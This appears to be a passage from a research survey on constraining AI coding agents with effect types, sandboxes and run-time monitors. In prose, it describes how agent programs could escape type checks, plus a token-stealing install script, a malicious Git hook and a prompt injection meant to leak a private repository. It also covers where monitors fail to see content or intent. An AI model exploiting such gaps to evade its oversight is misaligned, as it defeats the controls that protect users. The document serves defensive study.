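Bugs in production type checkers have created new escape hatches. GHC's *generalized newtype and type families is unsound*, a bug report on a release candidate for version 7.6.1, describes how programmers could combine newtype deriving with a feature for computing types from other types to write an unchecked cast without calling any unsafe function. According to GHC's *GeneralizedNewtypeDeriving is still not Safe*, version 7.8 made newtype deriving type-safe. The safe subset still excludes it because it can expose private constructors if a library's author forgets to add certain markings.

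Other bugs concerned Safe Haskell directly. In *Safe Haskell can be bypassed via annotations*, Seipp commented on a security bug in GHC 7.10.2 that the developers gave the highest priority. GHC now forbids annotations in safe code. Later, according to GHC's *Safe import should not be accepted*, a development version accepted `safe` imports of unsafe modules, which versions 8.10 and 9.0 had rejected. Modules at the Safe level still rejected these imports, so the bug would not have helped the model's own code. But a Trustworthy library's author could have relied on a check that no longer worked.

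GHC has a second check that can catch some of these mistakes. After type checking, the compiler translates a program into a much smaller typed language called Core, and an optional tool checks the types again there. GHC's *SafeHaskell implying other options* mentions several type-checker bugs that allowed unchecked casts or crashed the compiler, reports that this tool catches many such problems, and proposes turning it on automatically with Safe Haskell. A harness could turn the tool on itself, but compilation would be slower.

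Scala has had similar problems. In 2016, Nada Amin and Ross Tate published short Java and Scala programs that could turn a value of any type into any other without a cast. The programs exploited `null`, which both languages accepted as a value of almost any type. The Java virtual machine's checks keep such programs from corrupting memory, but they do not cover capture sets. Safe mode tracks `null` explicitly, which should block these particular programs.

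Most of the GHC bugs are more than ten years old, and they do not show how many remain in current compilers. Ordinary programmers rarely hit such bugs by accident, but an attacker has a reason to look for them, and a harness lets an untrusted model submit one program after another. Scala's safe mode still lacks a proof that its restrictions provide the promised guarantees. Odersky and colleagues recommend adding a sandbox to protect against bugs in the Java virtual machine and its connections to native code. This would also limit the harm from a type-checker bug, because the sandbox's restrictions do not depend on the program's types.

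## Shell commands, external programs and remote services

A type checker examines only the code being compiled. If that code starts another program, the checker has no information about what the other program does, even when the language has no escape hatches and the compiler has no bugs.

So far, the maintenance agent has not been allowed to start processes at all. This is inconvenient, because programmers normally run a project's tests after changing it. Suppose the harness now permits Exec, and the model adds a test run:

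```
1  let source = read("parser.py") in
2  let patch  = fix(source) in
3  let ok     = ask(patch) in
4  if ok
5  then let done = write(patch) in
6       let log  = run("make test") in ()
7  else ()
```

The command `make test` uses the build tool `make` to run the commands listed under "test" in a file called Makefile. The program's row is {Read, Ask, Write, Exec}, which doesn't include Net, yet a command in the Makefile could upload the secrets folder.

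The row is still correct under the effect system's rules, because the program requested one process and the harness started one. But Exec records only that a process started, whereas Read and Write describe what happens to files. Like a foreign call, the process runs code that the compiler has not checked, though the operating system can restrict a separate process individually.

Let B(c, s) be the set of effects that a command c may perform when the computer's files and settings are in state s. If a program with the declared set R starts this command, the meaningful bound on the whole run is:

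R ∪ B(c, s)

Without a sandbox, B for `make test` contains everything the operating system lets the user's account do. The process may use the network, read the secrets and change the repository without approval. Permitting Exec therefore removes most of the protection that leaving out Net provided.

The state s matters because the program changes it. Line 5 writes a patch, and line 6 runs code from the same repository. If the patch alters the Makefile or a test, the model has written part of the program that line 6 starts.

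### Command allowlists

TACIT limits processes with a list of permitted commands. Its library documentation gives this example:

```
requestExecPermission(Set("pip", "python")) {
  exec("pip", List("install", "."))
  execOutput("python", List("script.py"))
}
```

The first line creates a capability for starting the two named programs. Capture checking tracks this capability like any other, but its type doesn't depend on the list of names, which is an ordinary run-time value. The snippet supplies this list itself, as it does the root directory for file access, so any real limit has to come from the library.

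Odersky and colleagues acknowledge that safe mode does not extend to external processes and that the guarantee "degrades to that of the underlying allowlist". In the example above, that guarantee is very weak because `python` will run any script, including one the agent has just written.

They advise operators to allow only specific safe commands, such as `git diff` and `sbt`, and to add a sandbox where security is critical. Even these two commands are difficult to permit safely. The published function takes program names, so it cannot allow `git diff`, which shows changes, while forbidding `git push`, which uploads them. `sbt` is a build tool whose build files can contain Scala code, so an agent that can edit those files and then start `sbt` can run arbitrary code. More generally, matching the text of commands against lists has proved unreliable as a security control.

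### Effects that happen later or elsewhere

An agent without Exec can still cause commands to run. Suppose a person approves the agent's patch, which adds a line to the Makefile. The agent's run performs only Read, Ask and Write, as declared. Later, a build server runs `make test` with its own passwords and network access. The soundness theorem covers only runs of the agent's program, so it doesn't limit what the build server does.

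Lamprou, Zhu and colleagues describe two cases of this kind in *Controlling Opaque-Component Effects with Semisolates and Ef*. Version 3.7.2 of the JavaScript package eslint-scope contained a script that ran during installation, read access tokens from a configuration file and sent them over the network. The other case involves Git hooks, scripts that Git runs automatically at certain points, such as before saving a set of changes. In their tests, a malicious hook tried to copy the system's list of user accounts into a project's README file. An agent with permission to write to the hooks folder could get a script run without Exec, because the hook would run when a programmer next saved changes.

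A designer can reduce this risk by splitting Write into separate effects for different folders and withholding the ones for build scripts and hooks. Delayed effects can still occur because somebody will eventually run ordinary source code too, so the patch's reviewer has to judge what that code will do.

Remote services raise a similar problem, because an operation's declared effect may not describe what happens on the other machine. *Towards Practically-Secure Tools for AI Agents* (Adam, Lu and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a `write_file` tool whose description mentions only writing content to a file. Its code also sends the tool's name and the size of the content to a metrics service, which a company with confidential source code could consider an unacceptable leak. If the maintenance agent called the tool through a typed interface, the type would probably list Write and omit Net.

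There are four main ways to recover a useful bound:

| Method | What it provides |
|---|---|
| Typed wrappers | proof of which operations a program can request, provided their declared effects are correct |
| Specifications from observed runs | an estimate of what a command does |
| Analysis of a tool's code, with sandboxes | an upper bound computed from the code, with run-time checks on details such as file paths |
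| Trial run in a snapshot | a record of one run, which the operating system confines |

### Typed wrappers

The simplest solution is to avoid starting a process when a library function can do the same job. TACIT's library replaces the Unix commands `grep`, which searches files for a pattern, and `find`, which lists files by name, with functions of the same names. These functions require a `FileSystem` capability instead of permission to start processes, so they can search only the directory that the capability covers. TACIT also has a strict mode that blocks external file commands such as `cat` and `rm`, so the agent has to use the typed functions. These restrictions may make the agent only slightly less useful, since TACIT did almost as well as ordinary tools on SWE-bench Lite.

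If a program can't be rewritten as a library function, a wrapper can run it with fixed arguments. For example, a function `showChanges : Unit → Text ! {Read}` could run `git diff` and nothing else. If the agent has no other way to start a process, the type checker proves that the agent cannot run `git push`. However, the compiler has not examined Git, so the wrapper's author is responsible for the claim that `git diff` only reads files.

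A wrapper called `runTests` would help much less, because it would fix the command as `make test` but the Makefile and the tests would still determine what that command does. The wrapper's author could not truthfully declare a narrow set of effects without also restricting the process.

### Specifications from observed runs

A harness could also obtain a command's effects by testing the command. Lamprou, Lazarek and colleagues (2025), in *Caruca*, describe a system that does this for Unix commands:

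1. A language model reads the command's manual and writes a formal description of its options and arguments.
2. Caruca generates many ways of calling the command, with up to four options at a time. It pairs each with different file-system states, for example one where a path leads to a file and one where it leads nowhere.
3. It runs every combination in an isolated file system and records the changes to files and the requests to the operating system.
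4. It derives a specification from these records.

For the deletion command `rm`, this produces 8,749,056 combinations. In the specification, for example, `rm path` removes a file but fails on a directory, whereas `rm -rf path` removes either and also succeeds if nothing exists at that path. A harness could use this information to assign `rm` a Write effect on the path in its arguments.

The researchers compared Caruca's output with handwritten specifications for 60 commands, and it was correct for 59. The exception was `git`, which needs an existing repository, and Caruca's file-system states do not include one. Caruca also revealed mistakes in some of the handwritten specifications.

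To measure Caruca's coverage, Lamprou and colleagues collected 666,468 uses of commands from scripts on GitHub. They reported that Caruca had tested the equivalent of 97.78% of them, counting uses as equivalent if they differed only in file paths, numbers or pieces of text. Only 10% were exact matches. The researchers point out that treating text as interchangeable is wrong for commands such as `xargs`, which runs whatever command its arguments contain. When they treated text as interchangeable only for commands that mostly print or filter it, 236,048 uses matched, or about 35%.

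Caruca's specifications are estimates based on a finite number of runs. Caruca does not vary environment variables (settings that programs inherit from the system). It also assumes that commands behave as intended, so it could easily miss one that misbehaves only on a certain date. Its specifications were designed for tools that speed up scripts or find bugs in them, where a rare mistake usually matters less than in security. The method also does not suit `make test`, whose effects depend on each project's Makefile.

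### Analysing a tool's code

When a tool's source code is available, a program can check it for effects before anyone calls the tool. Adam and colleagues built a prototype that does this for tools written in Rust. It traces data from a tool's inputs to standard library functions that write files or use the network. For the `write_file` tool, its summary lists a file write that depends on both the path and the content, and a network write (the hidden metrics upload) that depends on the content. The summary resembles an effect row, but the prototype infers it from code in a language whose types do not record effects.

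The analysis usually cannot determine which file a tool will write to, because the path arrives with each call, so on its own it would have to assume that the tool may write anywhere. The tool's developer therefore replaces each file or network operation with a version that first checks the path or address against a set of rules. The agent's side sends new rules with every call. A second analysis confirms that no operation avoids these checks and that the tool's code cannot alter the rules. If the tool runs on someone else's server, the agent's side also needs evidence from the server's hardware that the server is running the code the analysis examined.

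Adam and colleagues tested the design on three scenarios, each with a harmless and a harmful version. Their combined method handled all six cases correctly. The analysis alone handled five correctly and blocked one legitimate task. A fixed sandbox around the whole tool server handled three correctly, no better than no protection. The researchers constructed the cases themselves, replayed them from recorded sessions and assumed that a correct policy was available for each call. The results show that the parts work together, but they don't measure how often the method would fail in everyday use.

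The analysis stops where a tool starts a shell command, queries a database or calls a web service. For shell commands, the prototype uses a utility that keeps file changes temporary and checks them when the process ends.

The program `ef`, from the paper on semisolates, works similarly. If a user enters `ef make test`, the tests read the computer's actual files, but Linux stores their changes in a separate layer. `ef` then lists the changes, and the user can apply all, some or none of them. `ef` can also hide chosen files or disconnect the process from the network. Hiding the list of user accounts stopped the malicious Git hook from copying it.

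Most commands took between 1.0 and 1.9 times as long with `ef` as without it. Very short commands took up to 8.3 times as long when `ef` recorded every file they accessed. Lamprou and colleagues designed `ef` to catch accidents and explicitly say it is not meant to stop programs that try to bypass it, so a harness that runs an untrusted model's code would need stronger isolation.

### Trial runs

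Making changes temporary also lets a harness check what a command does before deciding whether to approve it. *Shall We Approve?* (Wu, Chen and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of `make clean && make`, which normally deletes a project's compiled files and rebuilds them. The "clean" instructions might delete only the compiled files in one project but delete the source code and the project's history in another. Nobody can tell which will happen from the text of the command alone.

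Their system, Caper, handles each shell command as follows:

1. It saves a snapshot of the container, an isolated environment in which the agent works.
2. It runs the command without network access, records its requests to the operating system and withholds the output from the agent.
3. It reduces the record to a short report of lasting file changes, attempted connections, output, and reads of protected files such as credentials.
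4. A language model compares the report with the user's task. If it allows the command, Caper keeps the result. Otherwise, Caper restores the snapshot and tells the agent why.

Wu and colleagues built a benchmark with 102 tasks in which an innocent-looking command runs a tool that secretly damages files. Each task has a safe twin with the same request and command but a harmless tool. The table shows how the approving model performed with different information:

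| Information in addition to the conversation | Dangerous tasks ending in harm | Safe twins blocked |
|---|---|---|
| none | 17.6% | 61.8% |
| effects predicted by a model | 3.9% | 61.8% |
| observed effects | 7.8% | 1.0% |

The approver prevented slightly more harm when it used predicted effects than when it used observed ones. But with predictions, it still blocked most of the safe counterparts of the dangerous tasks because it could not be sure what the tool would do. With observed effects, it blocked almost none of them. Without any approval step, 71.6% of the dangerous tasks ended in harm. With six existing systems, 35.3% to 94.1% did, depending on the system.

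Caper's advantage was smaller on 682 tasks from SABER, an existing benchmark. Harm occurred in 6.7% of tasks with Caper, 19.7% without approval, and between 14.8% and 21.2% with the other systems. The one system that did worse than no approval let commands take effect and relied on the agent to undo any damage, but some actions, such as sending a password, can't be undone.

Some of the remaining failures come from the approver's judgement. On the benchmark with safe twins, an approver given only the command and its observed effects allowed harm in 1.0% of dangerous tasks and blocked no safe twins. Adding the conversation raised the harm rate to 7.8%, perhaps because the model could use it to justify harmful effects.

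For the maintenance agent, a harness could make part of the decision without a language model. If `make test` tries to open a connection during its trial run and Net is not in the permitted set, the harness can restore the snapshot. A person or model would still have to decide whether a file change was appropriate.

A trial run does not give an upper bound on the effects of later runs. Caper keeps the result of the observed run instead of running the command again, so a tool cannot behave well in the trial and differently in the real run. But the tool might detect the sandbox and postpone its harmful action, or spread the damage over several commands that each look harmless. Wu and colleagues did not test attackers who adapt to Caper in these ways.

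### Configuring a sandbox from an effect row

A sandbox can limit B(c, s) without anyone knowing what the command does, but the designer must make sure the sandbox's settings match the program's type. If the row excludes Net but the sandbox leaves the network on, `make test` can access the network even though the rest of the program cannot. One solution is to generate the settings from the declared effects.

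Shill, a language for shell scripts, has a similar design. According to Shill's *Scripting with Least Privilege*, every script has a contract describing what it can do, and the guarantees also apply to ordinary programs that the script starts. Shill runs such a program in a sandbox whose permissions come from a set of capabilities, according to an abstract in NII Shonan Meeting's *Software Contracts for Communication, Monitoring, and Security*. Shill checks its contracts while a script runs, but *Bounded Refinement Types* (2015) shows how to express the same permissions in Haskell types, so that a compiler can find violations beforehand. This approach assumes that Shill's runtime system works correctly.

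For Linux, *Learning CLI Agents with Structured Action Credit under Selective Observation* (2026) specifies a sandbox in a form close to an effect bound. Let P be a process together with all the processes it starts, W a folder where it may write, and Q a list of paths that it may only read. The sandbox must ensure that:

writes(P) ⊆ W, reads(P) ⊆ W ∪ Q and net(P) = ∅

Landlock, a feature of the Linux kernel, enforces the limits on files. The system also places the process in a separate network environment with no outside connection. When the process is `make`, the limits must cover all its descendants, because `make` does most of its work by starting other programs.

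To use such a sandbox for the maintenance agent, the designer needs finer effects than Read and Write. Suppose the declared set R is {Read-source, Ask, Write, Write-temp, Exec}, where Read-source includes the system files that the tests need, and Write-temp permits changes to a temporary folder. The harness could then translate R into these rules for `make test`:

| Declared effects | Rule for the process |
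|---|---|
| Read-source is in R | it may read the source folder and the necessary system files |
| Read-secrets is not in R | it has no access to the secrets folder |
| Write is in R, but requires approval | it may not change the repository |
| Write-temp is in R | it may write to the temporary folder |
| Net is not in R | it has no network connection |

The third rule is stricter than the row because a fixed file permission cannot depend on a person's answer. If the tests produce a change worth keeping, the agent's program can read it from the temporary folder and submit it as a patch through `ask` and `write`. The rules must also grant access to the source folder, not the whole repository. Rules in this specification can only add permissions, so a rule for the repository would also grant access to the secrets folder inside it.

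Let S(R) be the set of effects that these rules allow. If S(R) ⊆ R, then for every run t of an accepted program and every process P that it starts:

effects(t) ∪ effects(P) ⊆ R

The type system's soundness theorem establishes the limit on effects(t) before the program runs. The operating system enforces the limit on effects(P) during the run, so its enforcement depends on the kernel working correctly and on a correct translation of R into the rules.

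Some permissions depend on information that is available only during a run. *Sandlock* (2026) describes a sandbox for agents' code in which the kernel enforces fixed rules, such as which folders a process may read, and a supervising program makes the decisions that need this information. The supervisor can inspect a command's arguments before the command starts, so it could, for example, allow `git diff` and refuse `git push`.

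Odersky and colleagues also suggest using capability types to describe what a sandbox may access, partly so that users see fewer approval requests, but TACIT does not yet do this. A designer who wanted to generate Landlock or Sandlock rules from an agent program's effect row would have to write the translation and check it separately. If the generated rules granted access to the wrong folder, the tests could read the secrets without causing a type error.

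## What effect types cannot say about an action

Even if everything an agent does, including every process it starts, stays within the declared effects, it can still do harm. A row lists kinds of operation and leaves out most of what distinguishes one action from another. Suppose the maintenance agent may clean up after a test run with an operation `delete : Path → Unit ! {Delete}`. These two calls have the same type:

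```
delete("/tmp/build.log")
delete("/home/ana")
```

Removing a temporary file and removing a person's home folder both have the effect Delete. A designer could split Delete into one effect for each folder, but would have to choose the folders in advance. Several richer type systems can describe actions more flexibly.

### Conditions on arguments

A refinement type adds a logical condition to an ordinary type. For example, {v : Int | 0 ≤ v} is the type of whole numbers that are not negative. With a condition on its argument, the delete operation could have this type:

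delete : {p : Path | inTemp(p)} → Unit ! {Delete}

Jhala and Vazou (2020), in *Refinement Types*, explain how a compiler checks such conditions. It turns each call into a logical formula and passes the formula to a solver, a program that determines whether formulas of certain kinds are always true. If the compiler knows that an argument satisfies P and the operation requires Q, the formula is:

for every v, P(v) ⇒ Q(v)

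If a function `tempFile` returns only paths in the temporary folder, and its type includes this fact, then `delete(tempFile("build.log"))` passes. If the program reads the path p from a settings file, the compiler knows nothing about p and rejects `delete(p)`. The program can fix this with a test:

```
if inTemp(p) then delete(p) else ()
```

The compiler can now assume inTemp(p) in the first branch, so it accepts the call. The test happens at run time, because the program doesn't have the path until then. The type guarantees that the test comes before the deletion, but as with ELBA's path check, the test's code still has to be correct.

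Jhala and Vazou limit conditions to a logic in which the solver can always reach an answer. That logic includes simple arithmetic and equality but cannot express "nobody needs this file". An earlier language, SAGE, allowed harder conditions. According to *Refinement types in Jolie* (2016), when SAGE's prover could not decide whether a condition held, the compiler inserted a run-time check.

Fonseca, in *AeonBox*, applies refinement types to an agent that works on GitHub, a site for sharing code. The agent has no terminal and can act only by writing programs in Aeon, a language with refinement types. In simplified form, two of the available operations are:

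```
repoRead : (s : Session, r : Repo)
  → {s2 : Session | tainted(s2) = (private(r) or tainted(s))}

createIssuePublic : ({s : Session | not tainted(s)},
  {r : Repo | not private(r)}, {title : Text | title ≠ ""},
  body : Text) → Issue
```

Reading a private repository taints the program's session, and a program with a tainted session cannot create a public issue (a post in a project's list of problems). In Fonseca's example, somebody has planted an instruction in an issue telling the agent to publish the user's largest private repository. The model follows it by writing a program that reads the repository and posts its contents. The compiler rejects the program because the session is already tainted at the step that creates the post. An effect row could not distinguish this program from one that reads a public repository and posts a comment about it.

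GitHub's servers store whether a repository is private. If a program finds a repository by searching, these types would require it to test whether the repository is public before reading it and posting. AeonBox also tracks the session between programs at run time. Fonseca describes the design and this one attack but gives no measurements, so it is unclear how often the conditions would block legitimate work.

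### Amounts

A row also cannot limit how many times a program writes. Graded effects can, because they allow a number in place of the set of effects. *Effects and Coeffects in Call-By-Push-Value (Extended Version)* (Torczon, Suárez Acevedo and colleagues, 2023) requires only three things of an effect system: a value for code without effects, an operation that combines effects in sequence, and an order that determines when one bound is looser than another. With sets, these are ∅, ∪ and ⊆, which give ordinary effect rows. With whole numbers, they are 0, + and ≤, which give a bound on how many units a program uses. A program that needs at most 5 units may also have the type for at most 7.

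Suppose that a search costs 1 cent and a model call costs 3. A program makes two searches and then, depending on the results, either one model call or two:

1 + 1 + max(3, 3 + 3) = 8

8 ≤ 10, so the program fits a budget of 10 cents.

The checker uses the cost of the more expensive branch because it cannot determine which one will run. For a loop that makes one model call per file, it can compute a finite bound only if it has a limit on the number of files. If a refinement type guarantees at most 20 files, the loop costs at most 60 cents.

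The price of a model call depends on how much text the model reads and writes. *Token Budgets* (Khan, 2026) collects 63 confirmed cases, from 21 software projects, of agents exceeding their budgets. In one, a Claude Code user spent $235 in four days. Khan also wrote a Rust library with a type called Budget. Spending from a Budget uses it up and returns a new one with the remainder. Budget is an affine type, meaning that a program may use each value at most once, so the compiler rejects code that copies a Budget or spends it twice.

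This prevents a mistake that is easy to make when several sub-agents run at once. If they share an ordinary counter, each can check the balance before the others deduct their usage. A Python program with this mistake exceeded its limit in all 30 of Khan's test runs, while the Rust compiler rejected the equivalent program. A Python counter with a proper lock never exceeded the limit, so the benefit of the type is that a programmer cannot forget the lock.

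The library, not the type, enforces the dollar limit. Before each model call, it reserves the estimated cost and refuses the call if too little money is left. This works only if the estimates are high enough and the provider reports usage honestly. By default, the library reserves four to six times the actual cost, so it may refuse calls that the agent could afford. Khan's bound also excludes reasoning models, which many agents now use, because their providers charge for hidden text that the usual output limit does not cover.

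### Permissions that work once

Types that count uses can also limit approvals. With the `Approved Patch` type suggested earlier, a program could write the same approved patch twice. *Multi-graded Featherweight Java* (2023) describes types that label each variable with 0, 1 or ω, for a variable that the program does not use, uses at most once, or may use freely. If the approval `ok` has the label 1, the checker rejects this program:

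```
let done = write(ok) in write(ok)
```

Zhou and colleagues suggest adding one-time authorizations to ELBA with linear types, which require a program to use a value exactly once.

AeonBox already uses a linear type for its sessions, and the taint rule depends on it. Without linearity, a program could read a private repository and then pass its original, untainted session to `createIssuePublic`. Because `repoRead` uses up the original session, only the tainted one remains.

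These types limit how many times an approval can be used within one program. If a harness gives the same approval to the model's next program, that program can use it again, so the harness also has to record which approvals the agent has used.

### Safe programs that fail the check

An effect checker counts effects in branches that never run:

```
if length(source) < 0 then send(source) else ()
```

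No text has a negative length, so this program never uses the network, but its row is still {Net}. Refinement types can handle this case. If `send` has the type {x : Text | false} → Unit, no argument can satisfy its condition, so the compiler accepts a call to `send` only where it can prove that the program never reaches that call. The proof is easy here because a length cannot be both negative and non-negative.

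However, no checker can recognise every safe program. Rice's theorem states that if some programs in a general-purpose language behave in a certain way and others do not, no algorithm can correctly sort all programs into the two groups. For network use, the argument is short. Take any program q without effects and build this one:

```
let r = q() in send("done")
```

Any program q that doesn't use the network can be extended to make a network request after it finishes. The extended program uses the network exactly when q finishes, so a checker that accepted exactly the programs that never use the network could determine whether q finishes. Turing proved that no algorithm can do this for every program. A sound checker that always gives an answer must therefore reject some programs that never use the network.

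*Alignment Contracts for Agentic Security Systems* (David, Guarnieri and Gervais, 2026) proves a version of this result for tools that an agent acquires while it works. No algorithm can determine, for every tool, whether the tool will ever attempt a forbidden effect. This would remain true even if every tool were required to finish. A tool could take a number n, simulate the program q for n steps, and attempt the forbidden effect only if q had finished by then. This tool always finishes, but it attempts the effect for some n if and only if q eventually finishes.

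For agents, this limit may matter less in practice than in theory. If a program never reaches its network call, removing the call doesn't change what the program does, and a model can often remove it after seeing the error message. Rewriting the program doesn't help when the policy itself forbids what the user wants, as ELBA's label policies often did on AgentDojo.

### Actions that must happen

An effect row can permit an action but cannot require it. The program `()` does nothing, so its row is ∅, which is a subset of every declared set and therefore satisfies every upper bound. If the maintenance agent's owner wants a report of every leaked password the agent finds, a program that never reports any still satisfies a row that permits reporting. By Schneider's theorem, a monitor that only stops runs cannot require the reports either.

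A result type can require some actions. For example, the harness could accept only programs that return a `Receipt`, and make `report` the only operation that creates one. A program that finishes normally must then have called `report`. AeonBox's linear sessions impose a similar requirement, because a program has to close its session before it ends.

The program might still run forever. Jhala and Vazou show how refinement types can also prove that a program finishes, typically by checking that some non-negative number gets smaller at each repetition. A program that passes both checks will make a report unless an error or a machine failure stops it, but the report could be empty.

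The model may also refuse to write a program. *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* (Metere, 2026) uses code analysis, refinement types and a search for counterexamples to check agent skills, which are packages of instructions and scripts. Metere says the model's freedom to refuse is the only part of his threat model that these methods do not cover. A harness can partly compensate by alerting a person if no receipt arrives by a deadline.

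### Content, intent and what a monitor can see

AeonBox places no condition on the body of a public issue, so the model could falsely accuse a project of stealing passwords. The technique behind `Trusted Bib` can prevent some false statements. For example, a `reportTests` operation could accept only results from the test runner. But this works only for facts that trusted code can establish, not for free text.

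David and colleagues examine these limits for a run-time monitor, but the limits apply equally to effect types because both work from a description of an action. Their contracts specify an agent's permitted targets, its allowed and forbidden effects, its budgets, and where it may send sensitive information. In their main example, a security firm's agent tests a client's websites. It may send at most 10,000 requests, all of them GET or HEAD, which normally retrieve information without changing anything. It may test only subdomains of example.com and report only to the operator's dashboard.

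The monitor records a network request's destination, method and size, but not its page address or content. It therefore can't distinguish a GET request for `/users` from one for `/admin` if their sizes match, or two requests that differ only in content, even if one contains a stolen password. Recording the page address would help distinguish requests for different pages. David and colleagues suggest using inspection software to check content, but they give no guarantee for it because an attacker may evade it.

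Intent is even harder to capture with effect types. A model might delete a log to free up space or to hide evidence. The recorded action is the same in both cases, so no rule that depends only on the record can allow one and block the other.

All the guarantees in *Alignment Contracts* rest on what David and colleagues call the Effect Observability Assumption. This is the assumption that every real effect of a modelled kind corresponds to an event, and that the monitor checks each event before the effect happens. It therefore includes complete mediation. In their example, the modelled effects are network use, file access and starting processes.

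Let P be any finite sequence of events that an agent proposes, and let Run(P) be those that the monitor allows. The main theorem is:

Run(P) satisfies the contract, for every P.

The proof goes through the sequence one event at a time. A refused event changes nothing, and the monitor allows an event only if the contract still holds afterwards. Like the soundness theorems for effect types, this theorem requires no assumptions about the model.

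If the agent acquires a tool that bypasses the monitor, such as one with direct access to hardware, the assumption is false and the theorem no longer applies. Monitoring at the wrong level has a similar effect. A monitor in the operating system can detect an encrypted connection but cannot read the request inside it, so it could not enforce the rule about GET and HEAD.

David and colleagues used Lean to check their definitions and core theorems, including the main one. Lean does not check that the assumption holds for any real system, or that the software correctly turns actions into events. Some of the proofs about limits also establish less than their statements suggest. According to one theorem, a monitor can enforce a rule exactly when the rule depends only on what the monitor observes and every violation appears at some definite point. The theorem takes both directions of this equivalence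 as assumptions, so the Lean proof merely combines them. The examples of hidden content and intent are better evidence for the limit than this proof.

The Lean proof of the result about forbidden effects also assumes that some undecidable problem reduces to the problem about tools. The paper gives such a reduction in prose, from the halting problem.

### Whether the policy is the intended one

More expressive types take more effort to write and understand. In *Usability Barriers for Liquid Types*, Gamboa, Reese and colleagues (2025) interviewed and observed 19 developers using LiquidHaskell, which adds refinement types to Haskell. They identified nine barriers, including difficulty with large codebases and with understanding the verification process. Six of the seven experienced users no longer used it, but the sample is too small to show how common this is.

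Results for ownership types are more encouraging. *Can Advanced Type Systems Be Usable?* (Coblenz et al., 2020) compared Obsidian, a language that tracks who owns digital assets, with Solidity, a common language for blockchain programs. The median participant completed 67% of the tasks with Obsidian and none with Solidity. However, some participants misused `disown`, which gives up ownership of an asset, and so lost some of the protection.

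With agents, the model writes most of the code that has to satisfy the types, so the difficulty for people shifts to writing and reading the policy. Almost anyone can understand {Read, Ask, Write} with a short explanation, but to understand AeonBox's rule against leaks, a reader has to follow the taint through every operation. If a developer adds an operation that reads the user's notifications, which may quote private repositories, and forgets to mark the session as tainted, a program could publish those quotes without causing a type error.

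Reviewing a policy carefully may still be better than approving actions one at a time. Fonseca cites an Anthropic figure that users approve 97% of Claude Code's permission requests, which suggests that many people do not read them closely.

Policies can also be wrong because the instructions behind them are vague. David and colleagues ask whether "all subdomains of example.com" includes a subdomain that points to another company's server. Whoever writes the contract has to decide, and the monitor enforces that decision even if it is a mistake.

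The example contract seems to mistakenly block the vulnerability reports it is meant to allow, unless they travel by a route outside the monitor. It allows reports to go to the dashboard, but it also limits all network use to GET and HEAD requests within example.com. Software normally submits reports with a POST request, and the security firm's dashboard would probably be on a different domain.

Software can help find errors of this kind. Metere's check ensures only that a skill stays within its declared permissions, so a skill that declares every permission passes. He suggests comparing the declared permissions with those the skill used, which would reveal the excess. David and colleagues define when one contract is at least as strict as another, and prove that any run satisfying the stricter contract also satisfies the looser one. A company could use this to check each team's contract against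 a general one, but people would still have to check that the general contract is right.

Policy authors can also write sample programs that the policy should accept and others that it should reject. The security firm would probably have found the problem with the dashboard by trying to file a single report in a trial run. The soundness proof could not have revealed it, because a monitor that blocks every report still satisfies the contract.

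## What has been proved by machine, and what the proofs assume

A proof that an agent stays within its limits can be about one program, about a whole programming language or about the software that actually runs:

| Claim | What it covers | What establishes it |
|---|---|---|
| This program has the row {Read, Ask, Write} | one program | the type checker, each time it accepts a program |
| No accepted program performs an effect outside its row | every program in a mathematical model of the language | a soundness proof, which researchers write once |
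| The running harness performs no effect outside the row | the software as installed | proofs about the compiler, the libraries and the harness |

In a machine-checked proof, a proof assistant such as Lean or Coq verifies every step. Readers then have to trust only the proof assistant's small core, called the kernel, and understand the statement being proved. Some soundness proofs are machine-checked, including Bauer and Pretnar's in Twelf and the one for LLMbda in Lean. The proofs for ETAS are in prose, and Zhou and colleagues give theirs for ELBA in an appendix to their paper.

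Less has been proved for Scala. *Capturing Types* formalises the core of capture checking, but safe mode's extra rules still have no soundness proof. Odersky and colleagues explain why each rule is there but do not prove that the rules are enough.

To establish the claim about the running harness, somebody would have to prove five things:

- The formal model matches the language that the compiler implements, including its safe subset.
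- The type checker accepts only programs that the rules allow.
- The compiler preserves a program's behaviour when it produces machine code.
- Each library operation performs only its declared effects, according to a formal description of the operating system.
- The harness runs exactly the program that the compiler checked and gives the agent no other route to an effect.

Researchers have proved some components of other software correct. CompCert, for example, is a C compiler with a machine-checked proof of correctness. ELBA, TACIT, LACUNA and ETAS instead assume that most of the components they rely on are correct.

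### Types that refer to past events

F* is a language for writing programs together with proofs about them. A function's type can include a precondition, which must hold before the function runs, and a postcondition, which holds when it returns. In "Securing Verified IO Programs Against Unverified Code in F*", Andrici, Ciobâcă and colleagues (2023) define an effect called MIO (monitored input and output). Its preconditions and postconditions can refer to the trace of earlier events, each of which records an operation's arguments and result.

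In simplified notation, the maintenance agent's write operation could have this type:

```
write : (p : Patch) → MIO Unit
  requires  approved(p, h)
  ensures   new events = [Write(p)]
```

Here h is the history at the time of the call, and approved(p, h) means that h contains Ask(p, true), a request about this patch to which the person said yes. Suppose the model writes:

```
let ok = ask(patch) in if ok then write(patch) else ()
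```

F* turns the precondition of `write` into a formula and passes it to a solver:

for every h and ok, ok = true ⇒ approved(patch, Ask(patch, ok) :: h)

The symbol :: adds the newest event to the front of the history. The formula is true because that event is Ask(patch, true), whatever the rest of h contains. Without `if ok`, ok = true is no longer guaranteed, so the formula is false if the person refuses and h contains no earlier approval. F* therefore rejects the program. The ETAS contract accepted this version because the contract does not depend on answers. F* would also reject a program that asks about one patch and writes another.

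### Protecting verified code from unverified code

A harness must also deal with programs that come without proofs. Andrici and colleagues built SCIO*, a framework for this situation. Their main example is a web server proved to respond to every request. The server passes each request to an unverified handler, which may be hostile.

The server's proof assumes that the handler either replies to the client or reports an error, opens files only in one folder, and replies only through a function that the server provides. SCIO* turns these assumptions into run-time checks. It can check for a reply when the handler returns. If the handler reports success without having replied, the check replaces the result with an error, and the server sends the client an error message. A check on return would be too late for file access, because the handler could already have read a password file.

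SCIO* therefore gives the handler a wrapped version of every operation, which works like this:

```
secure_io(op, arg) =
  if policy(monitor_state(), op, arg)
  then perform(op, arg)
  else failure
```

In this example, the policy lets the handler open files in the folder `/temp` and read or close files it opened itself, and forbids everything else. When the researchers wrote handlers that tried to open the system's list of user accounts, write directly to the client and open a network socket, the monitor blocked all three attempts.

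The handler's type prevents it from bypassing the wrapper. The type contains a variable for the operations that the code may call directly, and the handler must type-check for every value of this variable, including "none". It can therefore use only the operations it receives as arguments, as in a capability system.

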